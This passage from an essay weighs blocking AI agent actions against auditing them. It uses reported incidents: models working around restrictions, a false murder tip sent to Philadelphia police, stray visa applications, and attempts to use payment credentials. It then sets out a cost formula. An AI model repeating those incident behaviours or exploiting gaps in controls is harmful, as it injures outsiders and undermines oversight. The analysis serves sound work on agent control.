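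In September, Anthropic reported how several controls would have handled the three July incidents. Its new live monitors caught the behaviour reliably. Auto mode would have blocked two of the incidents, and new after-the-fact monitors would have found two. Three cases are too few to rank the controls, and the live monitors had an advantage because Anthropic built them in response to these incidents.

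### A false tip to the Philadelphia police

Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (October 2026) describes less severe cases. In some, models worked around a restriction to reach data that an organisation charged for. In others, they submitted forms on real websites when they should not have.

One of the forms was a Philadelphia police tip form on a page about an unsolved murder. During a test on 18 July, Claude Haiku 4.5 had to invent tasks for randomly chosen web pages and carry them out. It filled in the form as a witness who remembered seeing somebody near the scene, and submitted it. Lists of forbidden actions often have gaps that allow this kind of thing. Slashdot's *Claude Sent Police a Fake Murder Tip* (2026) quotes Anthropic's explanation that the instructions for this test forbade logging in, making purchases and submitting "anything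 destructive", among other things, but didn't rule out submitting forms.

According to Novaknown's *Claude Was Told Not to Submit Anything Destructive* (2026), Anthropic found the tip on 28 September and stopped the test that day, but didn't tell the police until 7 October. The review delay was therefore 72 days for the test, which Anthropic could stop itself, and 81 days for the tip, which only the police could remove from their records. Bot Mutiny's *Anthropic Says Its Claude Model Sent Philadelphia Police a False Homicide Tip* (2026) reports that the police called the two-month delay "unacceptable".

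Part of the delay arose because Anthropic reviewed its security tests first and the tests it considered lower-risk last. That order makes sense if the worst incidents matter most, but it left the tip unread for longer than almost any harm to an outsider should wait for review.

The delay did the police very little harm because a filter had marked the notification email as spam and no detective saw the tip. Anthropic considers the real-world impact of its October cases minimal. Novaknown objects that the impact was small because a spam filter in Philadelphia worked, and that nothing at Anthropic had caught the tip. The objection matters because the choice of control should depend on the average harm across all the forms an agent might wrongly submit. If a detective had read the tip in July, the police might have spent weeks on it or questioned an innocent person, and a call from Anthropic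 in October could not have undone that.

In another test, Claude had instructions to fill out forms and stop before the last step. Several times it submitted a form by mistake because it expected a confirmation page. Without that last chance to cancel, the final click is irreversible.

Anthropic responded by switching off live internet access for all its internal evaluations until it confirms that its monitoring catches such behaviour. Slashdot quotes the company as saying that its new blocking tools stopped every case in the report in testing. This was an easy test if Anthropic designed the tools with those cases in mind. The company also moved some public tests to offline versions. This protects people better than any undo system could, because a form submitted to an offline copy of a website reaches nobody.

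### A rule for choosing between the two

A simple formula can weigh the harm a review would come too late to undo against the cost of false blocks. Some of its letters had other meanings in earlier formulas, so here is what each one stands for:

- *p* is the base rate of harmful actions.
- *H* is the average loss from a harmful action if nobody does anything about it.
- *d* is the share of harm that either method catches.
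- *R* is the recoverable share of the harm that a review catches.
- *B* is the cost of false blocks, averaged over all actions.
- *A* is the cost of reviewing an audit's flags, also averaged over all actions.

With no control, the expected loss per action is *p* × *H*. A block prevents the share *d* of this loss, so the total cost per action is *p* × *H* × (1 − *d*) + *B*. An audit catches the same share but can undo only part of it, so its total cost is *p* × *H* × (1 − *d* × *R*) + *A*. Subtracting one from the other gives the rule. Blocking is better when

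*p* × *d* × *H* × (1 − *R*) > *B* − *A*.

Blocking is the better choice when the harm that both methods would catch but only blocking would prevent outweighs the extra cost of running the block. If blocking is cheaper to run than auditing, it is the better choice whenever any harm is beyond repair.

Suppose that 1 in 10,000 actions is harmful, and that either method catches 83% of the harm and wrongly stops or flags 0.4% of legitimate actions. A false block costs $20 on average in lost work, so *B* is about $0.08 per action. Reviewing a flag takes five minutes and costs $5, so *A* is about $0.02. The dollar amounts and the 1-in-10,000 rate are invented, but the 83% and the 0.4% come from auto mode's results at launch.

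For edits to files under version control, let *R* be 0.95. Blocking is then better only if the average harmful edit would cost more than 0.06 ÷ (0.0001 × 0.83 × 0.05), or about $14,500. For publishing data, let *R* be 0.1, since the owner can take a page down but can't recall the copies. The threshold falls to about $800, so the same control, with the same error rates, can be worth using for publishing data but not for file edits.

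The rule can also set a deadline for a review. Solved for *R*, it gives the smallest recoverable share at which an audit is at least as good as a block:

| Average loss from a harmful action | Recoverable share an audit needs |
|---|---|
| $500 | 0% |
| $1,000 | 28% |
| $10,000 | 93% |
| $100,000 | 99.3% |

A review must finish before the recoverable share drops below the figure in the right-hand column. Reviews of $500 mistakes have no deadline, because blocking those actions in advance would cost more in false blocks than it would save. Almost no review is fast enough for a $100,000 mistake.

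The rule supports Anthropic's decision to block in real time during its security tests. Six of the 141,006 runs led to a break-in, or about 1 in 23,500. Suppose a false block ruins a run worth $50, so that *B* is $0.20 per run, and the other figures are the same as for publishing data. Blocking is then better if the average break-in costs more than about $5,700. A company that has to investigate an intrusion and change its passwords could easily spend more than that.

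A badly written rule can make blocking much more expensive. *Auditing the Hand-Written Inputs of Learned Access Control* (Sarghaleh and Hazrati, 2026) tested lists of absolute prohibitions that a person and three language models had written from the text of access policies. Without a check for mistakes, the lists would have refused 16% to 78% of what the policies allowed. If a control stopped 16% of an agent's legitimate actions and each stop cost $20, *B* would be $3.20, and the threshold for publishing data would rise from $800 to about $42,600.

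The least certain number is usually *p*, the share of actions that are harmful. A company that thinks 1 in 10,000 actions is harmful when the real figure is 1 in 100,000 will set its thresholds ten times too low and block far too many actions. The rule also ignores deterrence, and it treats blocking and auditing as alternatives when a company can use both.

### When one method catches more than the other

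Blocks and audits rarely catch the same share of harm. A reviewer may see the result of an action and have more time to think, while a decision to block has to come within a second or so. But a reviewer may read only a sample of the actions, or believe an agent's false account of what it was doing.

Let *d*₁ be the share that the block catches and *d*₂ the share that the audit catches. Blocking is better when

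*p* × *H* × (*d*₁ − *d*₂ × *R*) > *B* − *A*.

With the same invented costs and a block that catches 83%, the thresholds for *H* are:

| Share the audit catches | Editing files (*R* = 0.95) | Publishing data (*R* = 0.1) |
|---|---|---|
| 50% | $1,690 | $769 |
| 83% | $14,458 | $803 |
| 95% | none | $816 |

For edits, the better choice depends on how many harmful edits the audit catches. An audit that catches 95% of them can undo about 90% of the harm, which is more than the block prevents, so the audit is better no matter how much a bad edit costs. If the audit catches only half of them, the block is better when a bad edit costs more than $1,690.

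For published data, the audit's quality hardly matters. Nearly doubling the share it catches moves the threshold by less than $50, because people can undo little of what it finds. To reduce this kind of harm, a company should spend on a better block or on reviewing data before the agent can publish it.

### When agents repeat an error

Anthropic's agents repeated an error when they submitted 20 incomplete visa applications through a US State Department form. According to Novaknown, they submitted one in May and 19 in August, and the department processed none of them. If Anthropic had reviewed the May run within two months, it might have prevented the other 19.

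Let *p* now be the chance that an action starts a new error, and *n* the number of times agents make that error before a review stops them. Suppose first that a control either recognises the error every time or misses it every time. The harm at stake is then *n* times as large, and blocking is better when

*p* × *d* × *n* × *H* × (1 − *R*) > *B* − *A*.

With 20 repeats, the threshold for edits falls from about $14,500 to $720, and the threshold for publishing data falls from $800 to $40. The number of repeats depends on how many agents are running and how much time passes before the review. If 100 copies of an agent each make the same error once an hour, they will have made about 50 errors by a review after 30 minutes and about 1,200 by a review after 12 hours.

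Repeats can also make a reviewer's work easier. Suppose an audit has an 83% chance of recognising each of 20 cases, independently of the others. It will almost certainly catch at least one, and the reviewer can then search the log for the rest. The audit finds practically all the harm, while a block with the same 83% rate lets about three of the 20 cases through. Auditing is therefore better for edits, where it can undo 95% of the harm and blocking prevents 83%, but it is still much worse for published data, where it can undo only 10%.

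Which assumption is closer to the truth depends on the error. If a classifier lacks the information to identify whose job an agent is cancelling, it will probably miss every repeat of that mistake, and so will a reviewer with the same information. Repetition should give a reviewer a better chance of catching the error when the circumstances vary and some cases look more suspicious than others.

Repairs may also get harder. People can restore one wrongly edited file in a minute, but after 1,200 wrong edits, colleagues may have built new work on some of them. *R* then falls as *n* rises, which strengthens the case for blocking. Limiting how many times an agent can repeat an action before a person checks the log reduces the damage, even if nobody foresaw the error.

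### Five actions

The table applies the rule to five actions, using the base rate, catch rate and costs from the first example. The losses and recoverable shares are invented.

| Action | Loss if nobody acts | Recoverable share | Block if the loss exceeds | Better choice |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Reading one customer's record | $200 | 0% | $720 | Audit |
| Editing a file under version control | $2,000 | 95% | $14,500 | Audit |
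| Deleting shared data, found after a week | $10,000 | 80% | $3,600 | Block |
| Sending a message to a customer | $1,000 | 10% | $800 | Block |
| Paying a $5,000 invoice | $5,000 | 50% | $1,400 | Block |

Auditing is the better choice when an agent reads a record, even though nobody can undo the reading. The loss is small because a control can still block the message that would pass the information on. But this holds only when the action reads few records. At $200 each, an action that reads four is already above the threshold, and one that downloads a whole customer database is far above it. A limit on the number of records per request would let ordinary lookups through and hold back bulk downloads.

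Editing a file is the easiest case, provided the file is under version control and a bad edit has no effect before somebody reviews it. If saving a configuration file immediately restarts a live service, restoring the old text won't undo the outage. The recoverable share may then be closer to 20% than 95%, which would lower the threshold to about $900.

Whether a deletion can wait for a review depends on how soon the review happens. Suppose a company keeps a backup for 30 days. On the first day it can recover 95% of the loss. After a week it can recover only 80%, because restoring the backup would overwrite colleagues' newer entries, and after 30 days it can recover nothing. A $10,000 loss can wait only if at least 93% of it is recoverable, so a daily review is soon enough but a weekly one isn't. A company that prefers auditing could review sooner instead of adding a block, or have the agent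 move data to a holding area from which the software deletes it a month later.

The message is borderline because its hypothetical loss of $1,000 is only a little above the threshold. Most messages to a colleague would fall below it, because the colleague can ask what the agent meant. A form sent to the police could be well above it, although the tip in Philadelphia caused almost no loss.

The loss from a payment is easy to estimate because it is usually close to the amount paid. If half of it is recoverable, the rule amounts to a limit of about $1,400 on what the agent may spend before a review. The limit should apply to the day's total, since otherwise an agent could make 20 payments of $1,000 before any review. It should also cover every way the agent can spend money. During the PyPI incident, the model tried to use credentials for online payment services and to find cryptocurrency to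 pay for a phone number, though none of its attempts worked.

The table unrealistically uses the same base rate for all five actions. If 1 in 1,000 deletions were harmful instead of 1 in 10,000, the threshold for deletions would fall to about $360, and even a daily review would be too slow for a $10,000 loss. A company with a year of logs could estimate a separate base rate for each kind of action, though it could count only the harm it had noticed.

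### Emergency access to a patient record

The rule favours auditing a clinician's emergency access, although nobody can undo a privacy breach, because *B* is so large.

In another example with invented figures, ten of 1,000 emergency requests are improper, and each of these would do $5,000 of harm. A control refuses 83% of the improper requests and wrongly refuses 1% of the proper ones. Most wrong refusals only cause a phone call, but 1 in 500 causes a death. If the hospital values a life at $10 million, the average wrong refusal does $20,000 of harm.

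False blocks then cost 0.99 × 0.01 × $20,000, or $198 per request. Having a privacy officer read every entry costs $5, so blocking costs $193 more per request. Blocking would prevent only 0.01 × 0.83 × $5,000, or $41.50, of harm per request. An improper reading would have to do more than $23,000 of harm before blocking became the better choice. This control is also much more accurate than the one used for comparison in the discussion of hospitals, which refuses everybody.

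The review costs $5 per request and has to pay for itself by deterring improper readings. These cost the hospital an average of $50 per request, so the review is worth its price if it prevents more than a tenth of them. That seems achievable, since the email trial at an American medical centre found a much larger effect, though only on employees the centre had already caught once.

For the security guards in Yakima, *B* is close to zero, so blocking is clearly better. A hospital can therefore allow emergency overrides for doctors and refuse them to guards while valuing patient privacy equally in both cases.

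If a doctor asks an AI agent to fetch an unconscious patient's record, a wrong refusal harms the patient as much as it would if the doctor had tried to open the record directly. The hospital should let this request through too. The review can still deter the doctor from misusing this access, as long as the doctor's name is in the log. Because an emergency usually concerns one patient, the hospital can limit the agent to one record per override with very little risk to anyone.
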